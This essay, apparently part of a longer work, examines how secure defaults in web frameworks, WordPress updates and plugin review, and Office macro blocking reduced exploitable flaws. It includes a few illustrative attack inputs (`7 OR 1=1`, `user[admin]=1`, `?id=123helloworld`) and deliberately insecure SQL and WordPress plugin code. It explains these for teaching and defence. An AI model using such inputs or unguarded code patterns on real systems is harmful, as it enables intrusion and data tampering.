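All four opt-in failures involve passwords. A site should store passwords in a scrambled form that a thief who copies the database can't easily reverse. Four teams had a framework that offered this as an option, but all four stored passwords insecurely. All three teams with opt-in support for sessions used it. This may be because users can't stay logged in without sessions but can still log in if their passwords are stored badly.

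For each of the 91 vulnerabilities, Finifter and Wagner also checked whether the team's own framework offered a protection that would have prevented it. In 37 cases, the framework had a manual protection that the team had not applied. In only 2 cases, it had an automatic one, a category that here includes protections developers have to turn on. In 30 cases, the team had used the manual protection correctly elsewhere in the same program, so these programmers knew about the danger and how to prevent it but didn't apply the protection everywhere it was needed.

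The gap between 37 and 2 is less impressive than it looks because nearly all the frameworks offered manual protection or none against XSS and SQL injection, so the teams had little automatic protection to neglect. The count of 2 also seems to conflict with the four teams that ignored opt-in password storage. Finifter and Wagner write that they found no PHP framework with automatic support for storing passwords, but their table lists two PHP teams as having it. The count probably leaves those two teams out. If so, both of the counted failures involve opt-in password storage, and no vulnerability in the study got past a protection that was on by default.

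Finifter and Wagner call even their strongest results only suggestive. They tested 19 hypotheses and got three significant results, when chance alone would produce about one. The effects of the frameworks are also hard to separate from those of the languages, since both teams that were safe from CSRF used Java and both teams with faulty sessions used Perl.

None of the programmers was a novice. They averaged seven to ten years of experience, and their jobs required them to know about security, though the contest's instructions didn't mention security. Novices would presumably do worse with manual and opt-in protections. An always-on protection should work about as well for them as for experienced programmers, but this study could not test that.

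### CSRF on two lists

Larger datasets cover far more software but reveal less about individual frameworks. In *An Empirical Analysis of Input Validation Mechanisms in Web Applications and Languages*, Scholte, Robertson and colleagues examined more than 7,000 vulnerabilities caused by careless handling of input, and related them to the language each program was written in. They concluded that simple checks on the type of data would prevent most SQL injection and a significant number of XSS flaws. For example, a guestbook that looks up messages by number could refuse anything except digits. This would stop `7 OR 1=1`, the attack that got past PHP's magic quotes. A framework could run this check automatically once the developer declares that the field holds a number. A type check wouldn't protect a field for names, which has to accept the apostrophe in O'Brien. The study's conclusion is also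 an estimate, since it didn't compare programs with and without the checks.

OWASP's lists of the ten most serious web risks allow a rough before-and-after comparison for CSRF. OWASP added it in 2007 and still ranked it eighth in 2013, but dropped it in 2017. According to OWASP (2017), nearly 100% of applications had the flaw in 2007 and less than 5% had it ten years later. OWASP credits modern frameworks, with which developers are covered "without doing anything". Browsers can't have caused this decline, because Chrome did not start withholding login cookies from other sites' forms by default until 2020.

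The 5% comes from tests of over 114,000 applications, but the 100% is a recollection, and OWASP says it had no data on CSRF when it put the flaw on the list. The 5% may also be too low, because automatic tools have trouble detecting CSRF. Jeremiah Grossman, a security executive quoted in Dark Reading's *New OWASP Top 10 List Includes Three New Web Vulns*, was surprised that the flaw had been dropped from the list, because it was still common in older applications, which lack the built-in protection. He thought the data were partly biased toward modern software. This is a fair objection to the 5%, but it also supports the explanation, because the flaw persisted where the frameworks' protection was missing.

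The CVE catalogue seems to contradict OWASP. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), which is based on recent entries in the catalogue, ranks XSS first, SQL injection second and CSRF third. MITRE (2025) attributes 1,750 of the entries behind the list to CSRF, up from 1,301 a year earlier and five in 2006.

OWASP's figure is the share of tested applications that have the flaw, and many of those applications belong to companies that pay for testing. That share can fall even while MITRE counts many more reports, as in the invented guestbook figures in the first section. According to MITRE, the US government's catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers have exploited includes seven of these reports for XSS, four for SQL injection and none for CSRF. This is only weak evidence that CSRF attacks are rare, because a forged request looks like one that the user meant to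 send.

The decline in XSS is less clear. It fell from third place on OWASP's list in 2013 to seventh in 2017, according to OWASP's *Top 10-2017 Release Notes* (2017), but OWASP changed its method between the two lists. The announcement of the 2017 list cited Rails 3 and React, a popular tool for building pages, as reasons for hope, but added that a lot of vulnerable code was still in use.

### Code that does not compile

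Google went further than most frameworks and made the unsafe version of a query impossible to run. Kern (2025), in *Safe Coding*, describes how. The usual database command accepts any text, so it can't distinguish a query that the programmer wrote from one with a visitor's text pasted in. Google's version accepts only a special type, `TrustedSqlString`, which a program can assemble only from text in its own source code. In simplified form:

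```
// does not compile: name comes from a visitor
db.Query("SELECT message FROM entries WHERE name = '" + name + "'")

// compiles: the name travels separately
db.Query(trusted("SELECT message FROM entries WHERE name = ?"), name)
```

Compiling turns source code into a program that can run. A developer who writes an unsafe query gets a compile error within moments and has no program to test until the query is safe. Google handles XSS the same way, with special types for text that a page may display as HTML.

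Kern's *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* (2024) reports that ten years earlier, Google tended to find tens of XSS vulnerabilities a year in each large application such as Gmail. Hundreds of applications built on the new frameworks now average less than one report a year combined, and those that use the safe database interface have had no report of SQL injection for more than a decade. These figures count only reported flaws, but the low numbers are unlikely to reflect a lack of interest among outside researchers, because Google has paid them millions of dollars for XSS reports.

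Wang, Bangert and Kern, in *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, give figures for one product with a few tens of developers working on its client-side code. Outsiders reported ten XSS flaws of the relevant kind in the year before the product adopted the rules, two in the year of the changeover and one in the year after. The developers spent about a year cleaning up old code, which may have removed some flaws that the rules alone would not have caught. Across the company, a growing share of reported XSS flaws came from old code that didn't follow the rules, even as the amount of such code shrank, which is good evidence that new code had become safer.

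Some code needs the forbidden commands. Google's developers can ask for an exemption, but a security team decides, after checking whether the safe commands would do. In the early months the team received fewer than eight requests a week from a company with tens of thousands of developers, and by the end of 2020 less than 1% of JavaScript files had an exemption. By contrast, anyone who ran a PHP server could turn register_globals back on for convenience. Wang and colleagues list what makes their system easy to run, including compulsory code review, a shared store for all code and a single set of build tools. Novices working alone have none of these, and they can remove the check if it gets in their way.

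### The default that opened up GitHub

Frameworks can also create holes. Rails saved developers work with a feature called mass assignment, which copied every field of a submitted form into the database column of the same name. A page where users update their details needed only one line of code for this, however many fields it had:

`@user.update_attributes(params[:user])`

Suppose the form has fields for a name and an email address, and the database has an additional column, `admin`. A visitor who adds `user[admin]=1` to the request becomes an administrator. As with register_globals, an attacker could set a field that the form didn't include. Developers could list the columns that visitors were allowed to change, but Rails did not require a list. In 2008 a blog for Rails developers reported that four of the five most popular Rails applications were vulnerable (Willis, 2012, *GitHub incidents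 spawns Rails security debate*).

GitHub ran on Rails and hosted the Rails code. On March 1, 2012, a user named Egor Homakov asked the Rails developers there how the framework could force people to protect their sites. The next day he used the flaw on GitHub to file a bug report dated 1,000 years in the future. The Rails developers still closed the discussion. When Homakov cited his report as proof that the problem was widespread, one of them replied that they already knew about it, liked the protection as it was, and considered security the application builder's responsibility. On March 4, jtimberman (2012) noted that a three-month-old request to make the protection the default for new applications had also been closed a few days earlier.

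That same day Homakov used the form where GitHub's users update their public keys, which identify the computers that may change their code. He could assign his own key to another account by altering the field `public_key[user_id]`, which Exploit Intel's *CVE-2012-2055* names. He chose the Rails project's account and added a harmless file to its code. GitHub's *Public Key Security Vulnerability and Mitigation* (2012) says that the attack happened at 8:49 in the morning, that the flaw was fixed at 9:53, and that he had compromised three accounts. GitHub suspended him, then reinstated him after finding no malicious intent.

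The Rails developers changed the default almost at once, so that new applications had to list the columns visitors could change. Owners of existing applications still had to protect them themselves, and Willis reports that comments with false dates soon appeared on another Rails site, under an article about the affair. GitHub's developers were among the most experienced Rails programmers in the world, and they had overlooked a protection that took a few minutes to apply, so beginners could hardly have been expected to do better.

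### Who may delete message 7?

Under the new Rails default, developers still had to decide which columns visitors could change, because the right choice depends on the application. Visitors to a guestbook should probably be able to edit the text of their own messages but not the date, while visitors to an event-planning site may need to edit the date.

A framework can't supply access control rules on its own, because the right rules depend on what the site is for. On People by Temperament, two members may see each other's email addresses only after both have agreed. A framework can't enforce that rule unless a developer specifies it. Four of the nine teams left at least one hole that let a user get around the login or the access rules, and Finifter and Wagner knew of no framework that automatically prevented users from exceeding their permissions. They regard this flaw as fundamentally different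 from the others because preventing it requires a correct policy.

In code, the difference can be very small. Both of these Django lines fetch a message so that the program can delete it:

```
Message.objects.get(id=7)
request.user.messages.get(id=7)
```

The first line finds message 7 regardless of who wrote it. The second searches only the messages of the user making the request. Neither line contains anything a tool could flag as dangerous, and the first is correct on a page for moderators.

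Authentication, or checking who a user is, is much the same on every site, and frameworks have handled it better. OWASP's *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks* (2025) says that standardized frameworks appear to be reducing authentication failures, which rank seventh. Broken access control ranks first, as it did in the previous edition, while injection, which now includes XSS, has dropped from third to fifth. The order reflects OWASP's estimate of risk as well as frequency, so access control ranks first even though slightly fewer of the tested applications had a flaw in it (3.73% on average) than in encryption, which ranks fourth. Missing authorization also rose in MITRE's ranking, from ninth to fourth in a year. Such flaws are also common in applications built with AI.

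Frameworks can still help a little by refusing every request until the developer has written a rule for it. Google's frameworks also check requests centrally, although Kern notes that the details of the policy usually depend on the application. Refusing requests by default would make a missing rule show up in testing, as a missing CSRF token does in Django. But the quickest way to remove the error is to write a rule that allows everyone access, and the page will then pass all its author's tests.

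## WordPress: automatic updates and thousands of amateur plugins

A better framework protects new programs, but existing websites go on running old ones. The forum owners hit by the Santy worm could have installed a corrected version of phpBB a month earlier. Since 2013, WordPress, a free PHP program for building websites, has addressed this problem by installing security fixes automatically. It began as blogging software in 2003 and now runs 38.5% of all websites, according to survey figures cited in *WordPress core on US exploited-flaws list four times in 2026* (McSaveney, 2026).

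### The core and the plugins

Every WordPress site has the same core, and a group of trusted programmers reviews each change to it. Most other features, such as contact forms and online shops, come from plugins. Anyone may write one, and the official directory holds about 60,000. In *WordPress vulnerabilities in 2026*, an analysis of the free database WPVulnerability, Casares (2026) writes that plugin authors range from large companies to "a single developer in their spare time".

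WordPress loads a plugin's code together with its own, and the plugin can read and change the same files and database as the core. A hole in a plugin that makes snow fall across the page can therefore expose the whole site. Suppose the guestbook from the first section were a plugin:

```
add_action('wp_ajax_nopriv_delete_entry', function () {
    global $wpdb;
    $wpdb->delete('entries', array('id' => $_POST['id']));
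});
```

This code deletes an entry when a browser sends the right request. WordPress's `delete` function builds the query safely, which rules out SQL injection. But `nopriv` opens the request to visitors who haven't logged in, and the plugin never checks who sent it. WordPress has functions for checking permissions and CSRF tokens, but the programmer has to call them, and the delete button works without them.

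### Updates while you sleep

eWeek's *WordPress 3.7 Debuts, Improving Security for Millions* explains that before version 3.7, site owners had to click a button or download a new release to get a security fix. In October 2013, WordPress (2013) announced automatic updates with the phrase "Updates while you sleep". Sites now check WordPress.org twice a day and install any new maintenance or security release by replacing their own core files. These updates are on by default, but owners can turn them off with a line in a configuration file. They also fail on servers that don't let WordPress change its own files, which may be why WordPress promised them only for "most sites".

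Releases with new features are more likely to break something, and for years owners had to install those by hand. The developers copied security fixes to older versions so that people could keep using them safely. They still do this for versions as old as 4.7, from 2016, although WordPress (2025) describes such releases as a courtesy and officially supports only the latest version.

This makes figures on outdated sites easy to misread. The hosting company 20i analyzed 44 million sites and found that 88% were behind the latest release (Rijo, 2026, *20i finds 88% of WordPress sites running outdated software as attacks rise*). That figure includes sites on an older version that have every available security fix.

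The automatic updates that WordPress turned on by default in 2013 did not cover plugins. Since 2020, site owners have been able to turn on automatic updates for individual plugins. WordPress.org can also force a plugin update in an emergency. It did so in February 2022 for UpdraftPlus, a backup plugin with three million installations, because a flaw let any logged-in user download a site's backups.

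### How strangers edited other people's pages

Version 4.7, released in December 2016, switched on the REST API for every site. This feature lets other programs read and edit a site's content by sending requests to web addresses. To change post 123, for example, a program sends the new text to `/wp-json/wp/v2/posts/123`. WordPress should accept it only from a user with permission to edit that post. In simplified form, the code was:

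```
// may this user edit the post?
$post = get_post($request['id']);
if ($post && !user_may_edit($post)) {
    return error;
}

// edit the post
$id = (int) $request['id'];
update_post($id, $request['content']);
```

An attacker could add a second ID to the address, as in `/wp-json/wp/v2/posts/123?id=123helloworld`, an example from the CVE entry that Tenable's *CVE-2017-1001000* reproduces. WordPress used the second ID. No post has the ID `123helloworld`, so `get_post` found nothing, and without a post the code did not return an error. The code then converted the ID to a whole number. PHP does this by keeping the digits at the start and dropping the rest, so the ID became 123 and WordPress saved the attacker's text to post 123.

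Marc-Alexandre Montpas, a researcher at the security company Sucuri, alerted WordPress to a content injection flaw on January 20, 2017, according to *WordPress Fixes Security Flaw that Opened Users to Content Injection Attacks* (l33tdawg, 2017). Six days later WordPress released version 4.7.2, which contained the fix, but its announcement mentioned only three other flaws. WordPress (2017) did not disclose this one until February 1. Its security team used the delay to get as many hosting and security companies as possible protected, according to *Content Injection Vulnerability in WordPress* (Sucuri, 2017).

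Attackers then defaced so many pages that they were competing for them. *A Feeding Frenzy to Deface WordPress Sites*, by Wordfence, which sells a WordPress firewall, describes 20 separate campaigns. About two weeks after the fix came out, news reports put the number of defaced pages at over 1.5 million. The number of sites was much smaller, since a blog with 500 posts could account for 500 of those pages.

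Only versions 4.7.0 and 4.7.1 had the flaw. Every victim was therefore running a version less than two months old and had missed the next update, which means few of these sites can have been abandoned for long. Some owners had presumably turned automatic updates off, and some servers must have blocked them, but the proportions are unknown. The six-day delay in disclosing the flaw protected sites where updates worked but did little for the others.

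### Attacks on the evening of the fix

In July 2026 WordPress fixed wp2shell, a pair of flaws that together let an attacker take over a site without logging in. Adam Kues, who discovered one of the flaws, had used OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol Ultra to analyze the WordPress core and write a working attack, according to Expert Insights' *WordPress Force-Pushes Fix For WP2Shell*. WordPress lets a program send several requests in one batch. An attacker could make WordPress mix up the requests, so that a harmful value skipped the usual check and reached a database query. The 2017 flaw also involved a mismatch between what WordPress checked and what it acted on.

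WordPress released the fix on July 17 and forced automatic updates for the affected versions. Wordfence's *wp2shell Aftermath* (2026) records the first suspicious request at 23:29 UTC that evening and the first clear attempt at SQL injection 13 minutes later. The full technical explanation did not appear until July 20. Attackers had probably worked backward from the fix, which anyone could read because WordPress's code is public.

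It is unclear how many sites they broke into. Wordfence's *WP2Shell WordPress Exploit Technical Analysis and Real Attack Data* (2026) reports a high volume of attacks, but Wordfence expects that most sites were no longer vulnerable, because the flaws affected few versions and WordPress had forced the updates. A week after the fix, CanSSOC (2026), a security service for Canadian universities, warned that several attackers had succeeded. The web agency nebula.design, in *WordPress 7.0.2 Patches wp2shell*, could not establish whether the forced updates reached sites whose owners had disabled automatic updates.

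Automatic updates also help when the first fix is incomplete. In March 2026, WordPress (2026) found that a release from the previous day had not fully applied all its security fixes, and issued another release. Owners with automatic updates didn't have to do anything for either release.

But the updater can itself have a security hole. During a full update, WordPress unpacks the new version into a folder that is often reachable from the web. For a few seconds the folder contains a half-installed copy, and an attacker who reaches it in time can take over the site. A researcher at the security company Patchstack considered this attack impractical when WordPress fixed the flaw in October 2026. A week later Wordfence said it had blocked 13,095 attempts in one day, as McSaveney reports. Almost all attempts miss, but attackers can keep sending them to huge numbers of sites until they catch one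 in the middle of an update. Even so, the risk from updating lasts only a few seconds, while a site that stopped updating would be exposed for as long as its old holes stayed open.

The updater flaw was one of four flaws in the WordPress core that CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, added to its list of exploited vulnerabilities in 2026. They were the first core flaws on the list, which dates from 2021.

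### What the directory checks

Authors who want their plugin in the official directory must submit it for review. Since September 2024 an automatic tool, Plugin Check, has tested submissions before a human reviewer sees them. WordPress (2025) credits it with reducing issues at approval by 41%. The tool checks plugins against the directory's rules and general good practice, so the figure doesn't show how many vulnerabilities it kept out.

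For years, most plugins got no further review after approval. Developers could release a new version whenever they liked, and sites with automatic plugin updates would install it. In June 2024 an attacker exploited this by using leaked passwords to log in as the developers of several plugins, then releasing versions that created administrator accounts for the attacker.

Since June 2026, WordPress.org has held every new plugin release while several AI models and a malware scanner examine the changes, as WordPress' *Automated Security Review* describes. If the risk score is too high, WordPress.org withholds the release and emails the findings to the developers. Sites keep the previous version until the developers release one that passes. A novice who left out a permission check may get an email identifying the exact line.

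WordPress's AI review of plugins delays automatic updates by 24 hours, including security fixes, according to HostingAdvice's *WordPress Adds AI Plugin Reviews, Slowing Auto-Updates by 24 Hours*. Patchstack's *State of WordPress Security In 2026* (2026) gives a weighted median of five hours before mass attacks on a vulnerability begin. If the flaw is already public, a day's delay could leave sites exposed when attackers are most active. A false alarm that blocks the fix would leave them exposed for longer. Nobody has yet measured whether the review prevents more attacks than the delay allows.

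Reviewing plugin releases cannot catch changes that an attacker makes to a plugin on the website itself. In a 2022 study, Ranjita Pai Kasturi and colleagues at Georgia Tech examined backups dating back to 2012 from more than 400,000 web servers and found 47,337 malicious plugins on 24,931 websites. Most of the plugins had been harmless until attackers infected them after installation.

### The flood of submissions

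AI has made plugins much easier to write. The directory received about 150 submissions a week in 2024 and 330 by the end of 2025, according to WordPress's *A Year in the Plugins Team* (2026). In May 2026 it received about 700 a week. Nobody publishes a count of the AI-written ones, but Luke Carbis, a member of the review team, describes a flood of AI-generated plugins in an interview summarized by daily.dev.

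The queue of plugins awaiting review grew from about 300 at the start of February to 1,050 in mid-April, then fell to almost nothing within weeks, according to WordPress' *Update on the status of the team* (2026). The team had added three reviewers and was using AI to help with the checks. In May it did nearly 3,000 first reviews, up from 1,100 a year earlier and just enough to keep up with 700 submissions a week. WP Tavern's *WordPress Plugin Review Team Onboards New Members* reports that plugin authors had to wait at least 91 days during an earlier backlog in 2023.

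WordPress' *Plugins Team* (2026) lists 4,891 new and pending plugins on April 20, but only 827 were still waiting for a first response. Many of the others were probably waiting for their developers to make corrections. The team approved 257 plugins and rejected 282 that week.

So the review has kept pace, but these figures measure speed. They don't show how many vulnerabilities the reviewers found or missed.

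### Twelve thousand vulnerabilities a year

Casares gives these counts of published vulnerabilities:

| Year | Plugins | Themes | Core |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2013 | 382 | 124 | 35 |
| 2017 | 677 | 13 | 101 |
| 2021 | 2,172 | 164 | 24 |
| 2024 | 8,485 | 340 | 14 |
| 2025 | 10,519 | 948 | 18 |
| 2026, to November 21 | 10,925 | 1,111 | 84 |

Themes, the packages that control a site's appearance, can contain PHP code too. The 2026 total had reached 12,986 by the end of November, according to WPVulnerability's *How dangerous are WordPress vulnerabilities?* (2026).

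Casares attributes much of the growth to more people looking for flaws and more organizations issuing CVE numbers. Security companies pay for discoveries, with Wordfence (2026) offering up to $31,200 for a vulnerability. In one week of January, it added 321 vulnerabilities to its database, with contributions from 89 researchers. Wordfence and Patchstack both sell protection against the flaws they publish, so they have a commercial reason to find many, though their bounties also help developers learn of flaws they can fix.

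Estimates of the growth rate differ. Patchstack's total for 2025 was 11,334, up 42% from the year before, according to the software company Swif. Casares's figures show a 30% rise to nearly the same total.

The jump from 18 to 84 in the core is probably due largely to AI. WordPress's *The Core Security Initiative* (2026) attributes much of the increase in security reports to the growing ability of AI models to help with such research. The old code didn't get worse in 2026, but attackers can use the same models to find its flaws.

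The reported flaws are also becoming more serious. WPVulnerability finds that 44.3% of those with a severity score were rated high or critical in 2026, up from 29.4% in 2024. It reports fewer XSS and CSRF flaws and more authorization flaws, which would be consistent with ready-made protections working against XSS and CSRF. Bounties may contribute to this trend by encouraging researchers to look for the flaws that pay best.

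Harm has not grown at the same rate. Wordfence's *Quarterly WordPress Threat Intelligence Report* (2026) found that in the first quarter of 2026, published vulnerabilities rose 23.7% over the previous quarter, while infected sites rose only 1.4%, to 474,000. One quarter is too short to establish a trend, and some infections come from stolen passwords rather than vulnerabilities. The number of infected sites is still large, and it includes only those Wordfence knows about.

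### Plugins without an author

An automatic update can install a fix only if somebody has written one. The new review covers the changes in each release, so it misses any plugin whose author has stopped releasing updates. Of the 1,107 theme vulnerabilities that WPVulnerability lists for 2026, 740 have no fix.

Many abandoned plugins remain in use. Koudal (2026), in *Abandoned but still installed*, found 155 with at least 10,000 installations each and no release for two years, which makes at least 1.55 million installations. Some may be small, finished programs that need no changes. Vimsy's *WordPress Plugin Graveyard* (2026) lists 81 plugins that had gone more than a year without an update, 40 of them with known vulnerabilities. One is Limit Login Attempts, which people install to make their sites safer. Its last update was in April 2023, and more than 300,000 sites still use it. (Both lists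 come from companies that sell security or maintenance services for WordPress.)

The review team can close a plugin, as it did with 84 in that week of April 2026. This stops new downloads, but copies already installed keep running. Deleting them remotely could break a shop's checkout or a clinic's booking form. Each site's owner has to find out that the plugin is unsafe and replace it.

A hosting company's firewall might block an attack in the meantime, but when Patchstack tested popular hosts, their defenses stopped only 26% of its attacks on WordPress vulnerabilities. Patchstack sells a competing product and chose the attacks, so other tests might find a higher rate.

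## Office macros: from warning messages to blocking by default

Unlike WordPress plugins, which attackers exploited through mistakes in the code, Microsoft Office macros were dangerous even when written without mistakes. An accountant's macro for formatting the monthly figures seldom contained an exploitable hole. But it worked only if Office ran code stored in documents, and that meant Office would run an attacker's code too. Because many offices relied on macros, Microsoft left the feature on for everyone, including people who had never heard of macros.

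### How a document spreads a virus

In *Following the wrong script*, Arthur quotes a Microsoft marketing manager who says the idea for Office macros came from Bill Gates. Macros were meant to speed up repetitive jobs, such as formatting particular words or checking the fields of a submitted form. Spreadsheet users had the most to gain, because they often had to format many numbers the same way.

Word can also start a macro by itself. Suppose a clerk sends out a weekly report that takes its date and totals from other files. In the language Word has used since 1997, she can store this macro in the report:

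```
Sub AutoOpen()
    ActiveDocument.Fields.Update
End Sub
```

Word runs any macro named `AutoOpen` when someone opens the document, so a macro with that name can make sure readers always see the current totals. A macro can also replace a menu command that has the same name. Ducklin (2022), in *At last! Office macros from the internet to be blocked by default*, gives the example of a company that wants to stop people from printing confidential documents by mistake.

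The Concept virus of 1995 used both features. *What a (Winword.)Concept* (Gordon, 1995) explains how it worked. When someone opened an infected document, Word ran its `AutoOpen` macro without asking. The macro copied the virus into Normal.dot, the template on which Word bases new documents, along with a replacement for the Save As command that added the virus to every document the user saved with it. When the user sent one of these documents to a colleague, the process began again on the colleague's computer. Since the virus ran inside Word, it worked on Macs as well as on Windows.

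Concept did little else. Its `PayLoad` macro never ran and held only the comment "That's enough to prove my point". Gordon warned that a trivial change would make it do real damage, and that "any idiot" could copy the technique. According to Ducklin (2022) in *That didn’t last!*, Microsoft avoided the word "virus" and called Concept a "prank macro".

By early 1997 it had reached 49% of the sites in a survey by NCSA (1997), a computer security association. Macro viruses topped the yearly lists in Virus Bulletin (2000), a trade magazine, from 1996 to 1999. A wave of novices wrote viruses in the same simple language that let clerks automate their reports. According to the magazine, a schoolboy could learn to write one in a couple of weeks. Every copy of a virus also included its source code, which others could alter.

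ColdApe was the most reported virus in the magazine's 1999 figures, with 8,622 of 33,830 incidents. However, each infected computer sent a daily email to the virus expert Nick FitzGerald, and the magazine counted every email as a new incident. Without ColdApe, the most reported virus was Class, another macro virus, with 3,216 incidents.

### Melissa and the first warnings

Gordon suggested that Word should alert users when a document tried to change their global settings. Such an alert would have appeared for Concept but not for the clerk's report. Word 97 instead displayed a warning when a document contained any macro, and let users choose whether to run it. As Arthur points out, the warning could not show what the code would do, which made the choice hard if the document came from someone they knew.

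The Melissa virus, which appeared on March 26, 1999, reached people in emails from someone they knew. The subject line was "Important Message From" followed by the sender's name, and the text began "Here is that document you asked for". According to CERT (1999), a center at Carnegie Mellon University that coordinates responses to attacks, the attached Word document contained a macro that sent copies to the first 50 entries in each of the victim's address books. The macro also lowered Word's security setting, so the victim would see no more warnings, and infected Normal.dot, Word's default template. After that, it could send out the victim's own documents, including confidential ones.

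CERT knew of no new vulnerability that Melissa exploited. Word let any macro send email, change settings and copy itself, and Melissa's author combined these abilities. *Information Security* (Rhodes, 1999), testimony to the US Congress, says the virus had reached more than 100,000 computers at more than 300 organizations by the following Monday. One site received 32,000 copies in 45 minutes. Melissa did not normally delete anything, but it overloaded mail servers, and some organizations had to shut down their email. The FBI put the cost at $80 million, while Check Point Research's *The Death of “Please Enable Macros” and What it Means* (2022) mentions a reported $1.1 billion.

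Rhodes cited media reports that organizations fared much better if they had trained their employees and warned them about the attack. But he also said that the Department of Energy had considered the risk of damage low because Word would alert most users to the macro, and then found that Melissa had spread widely on its own sites.

Surveys of companies showed no sign that the warning was reducing infections overall. Stanford University (2000) gives the monthly infection rate per 1,000 PCs, measured each January and February, as 21 in 1997, 32 in 1998, 80 in 1999 and 91 in 2000. It attributes the 1999 jump to Melissa and to Happy99, a worm that did not use macros, but Melissa can't have contributed because it appeared in late March, after that year's measurements. The figures also include every type of virus, so the trend for macro infections may have been different.

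Word 2000 offered three security levels. Low ran every macro, Medium prompted the user first, and High silently ignored any macro without a digital signature from a source the user trusted. A signature shows who published a macro and that nobody has changed it since. Software companies could sign their macros, but the clerk with the weekly report probably had no certificate to sign with. If her colleagues chose High, her totals would stop updating without explanation, so Medium was the obvious setting for an office full of homemade macros.

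### "Please enable macros"

Macro viruses declined after 2000. Ducklin partly credits Microsoft, which made it harder for macros to copy themselves into clean documents. Check Point Research adds that criminals had started to write malware for money, and that macros could not record keystrokes or steal card details.

Microsoft also separated documents with macros from those without. Since Office 2007, Word files ending in `.docx` can't contain macros, while those ending in `.docm` can. This let mail filters treat the two differently without examining their contents. But Office still opened files in the old `.doc` format, which could be used with or without macros.

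In 2010, Office added Protected View, which opened files from the internet as read-only until the user clicked "Enable Editing". If the file contained macros, a second message then appeared, and the user could run them by clicking "Enable Content".

In the early 2010s, criminals began using macros to download larger programs that could record keystrokes or steal card details. This took only a few lines of code. The criminals mailed the document to each victim themselves, so the macro did not have to copy itself, and Microsoft's earlier measure against copying made no difference.

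The remaining safeguard was the buttons that readers had to click before macros could run. Criminals got past it by filling the document with a picture of an official-looking notice that told the reader to click, often with an arrow pointing to the right place. Tens of thousands of people clicked. Check Point Research jokingly calls this weakness "CVE-0", a vulnerability that nobody can patch.

From 2015 the company ran a program that automatically looked for such pictures and found hundreds of thousands of malicious documents, many of them missed by every antivirus program on the scanning service VirusTotal. The criminals responded by distorting the pictures so that people could read them but software could not, as in the CAPTCHA puzzles that websites use to keep out bots.

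The warning was what the first section called an opt-out protection, because macros stayed off unless the user turned them on. But opting out took one click, and the attacker could ask for that click in the document itself, directly below the warning. The user wanted to read what looked like an invoice or a court summons and had no way to judge the code. In an office where useful spreadsheets also arrived with macros, people would have seen the same warning every week and learned that enabling macros was harmless.

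### How Windows marks a file from the internet

In 2016 Microsoft gave administrators a policy that removed the button. Vumetric's *How to auto block macros in Microsoft Office docs from the internet* (2022) notes that the policy depends on a Windows feature, the Mark of the Web. When someone saves an email attachment or a download, Windows attaches a hidden label to the file. For a spreadsheet named `invoice.xlsm`, the label is in `invoice.xlsm:Zone.Identifier` and looks like this:

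```
[ZoneTransfer]
ZoneId=3
```

Zone 3 is the internet, zone 2 is a list of trusted sites, and zone 1 is the local network. The label doesn't depend on what the file contains, so a genuine invoice gets the same number as a fake one. It can also get lost, for example when someone copies the file to a memory stick with an older disk format. But it lets Office distinguish a stranger's attachment from a colleague's spreadsheet on the company server, so a company could block the attachment without breaking the spreadsheet.

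The policy was opt-in. According to Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office*, it works only with the enterprise version of the Office subscription, not the version for smaller businesses. Check Point Research asks what was supposed to protect a 17-year-old with a free antivirus program and no security department.

### Announced, paused and resumed

On February 7, 2022, Microsoft announced that Office would block macros in files from the internet by default, but only on Windows. Instead of a button to enable macros, users would see a red bar with a link to an explanation. Anyone who wanted to run the macro would have to save the file, open its properties in Windows and tick a box marked "Unblock". Macros would continue to run if they came from a trusted publisher or a trusted folder, or if the user had enabled them in that file before the change.

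Users of a preview version began getting the block on April 12. On July 6 a user, Vince Hardwick, asked on Microsoft's website whether the block had disappeared. A Microsoft employee confirmed that the company was withdrawing it and apologized for starting the withdrawal before announcing it. No Longer Set's *Microsoft Backtracks (Temporarily?) on Policy to Block All Macros* (2022) reprints the exchange. Microsoft then said that it had acted on user feedback and would make the feature easier to use. In AskWoody's *Dear Microsoft, don't give up on this please* (2022), one customer begged the company to keep macros off and let administrators turn them on where needed.

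Microsoft did not publish the feedback, and Malwarebytes (2022) found surprisingly little information about the reasons for the pause, even after the rollout had resumed. Ducklin concluded that many companies relied on macros from outside and weren't ready to change how they worked. Internal documents stored online were probably another problem. Many firms keep them on OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's storage services, and a browser may mark a file downloaded from there as coming from the internet. When an administrator asked about such files, Microsoft suggested adding the services' addresses to the list of trusted sites.

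The general rollout of the block began on July 27, three weeks after Hardwick's question, and reached customers on the slowest update schedule in January 2023. Office Watch's *Inside the Office VBA/Mark of the Web changes* (2022) compared the documentation before and after the pause and found about a thousand new words, most of them in a table on how to get around the block.

Organizations could still reverse the change, just as web hosts could turn PHP's register_globals back on. But a company that trusted its own file server did not expose anyone outside the company.

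### Where the attackers went

The security company Proofpoint counts malicious email by campaign, a group of related messages that its researchers have analyzed by hand. Vumetric's *No more macros?* (2023) reports that Proofpoint counted more than 700 campaigns with ordinary Office macros in 2021, and nearly as many with an older type specific to Excel. Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* (2022) found that the use of both types fell by about 66% between October 2021 and June 2022. For ordinary macros alone, Computer Weekly reports just under 70 campaigns in October and just over 21 in June.

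Nearly all of this fall came before the general rollout. Proofpoint attributes the fall to criminals reacting to Microsoft's announcements, the first of which covered the older Excel macros and came in October 2021. That is plausible, since gangs that rely on email attachments have good reason to test a replacement early. But a few large groups can shift these numbers by themselves. For example, use of the older Excel macros rose briefly in March 2022, probably because the group behind the Emotet malware was unusually active.

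The later figures are more convincing. Two companies with different customers and methods found that macros had almost disappeared from malicious email. IBM (2024) counted emails instead of campaigns and found 93% fewer with malicious macros in 2023 than in 2022, with almost none after March. Proofpoint also saw hardly any macros in early 2023, according to CyberScoop's *Cybercriminals have adapted since Microsoft’s decision to block macros* (2023).

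Criminals replaced them with a series of other carriers:

| Carrier | How it helped attackers | What happened next |
|---|---|---|
| Disk images | Files inside them did not get the Mark of the Web | Use fell after a Windows update in November 2022 |
| Shortcut files | Opening one can run a command | Use peaked in June and September 2022 |
| Web pages as attachments | The page assembles the malware on the victim's computer | Down 96% in 2023 |
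| OneNote notebooks | They can contain other files | Large campaigns in early 2023, very few after March |
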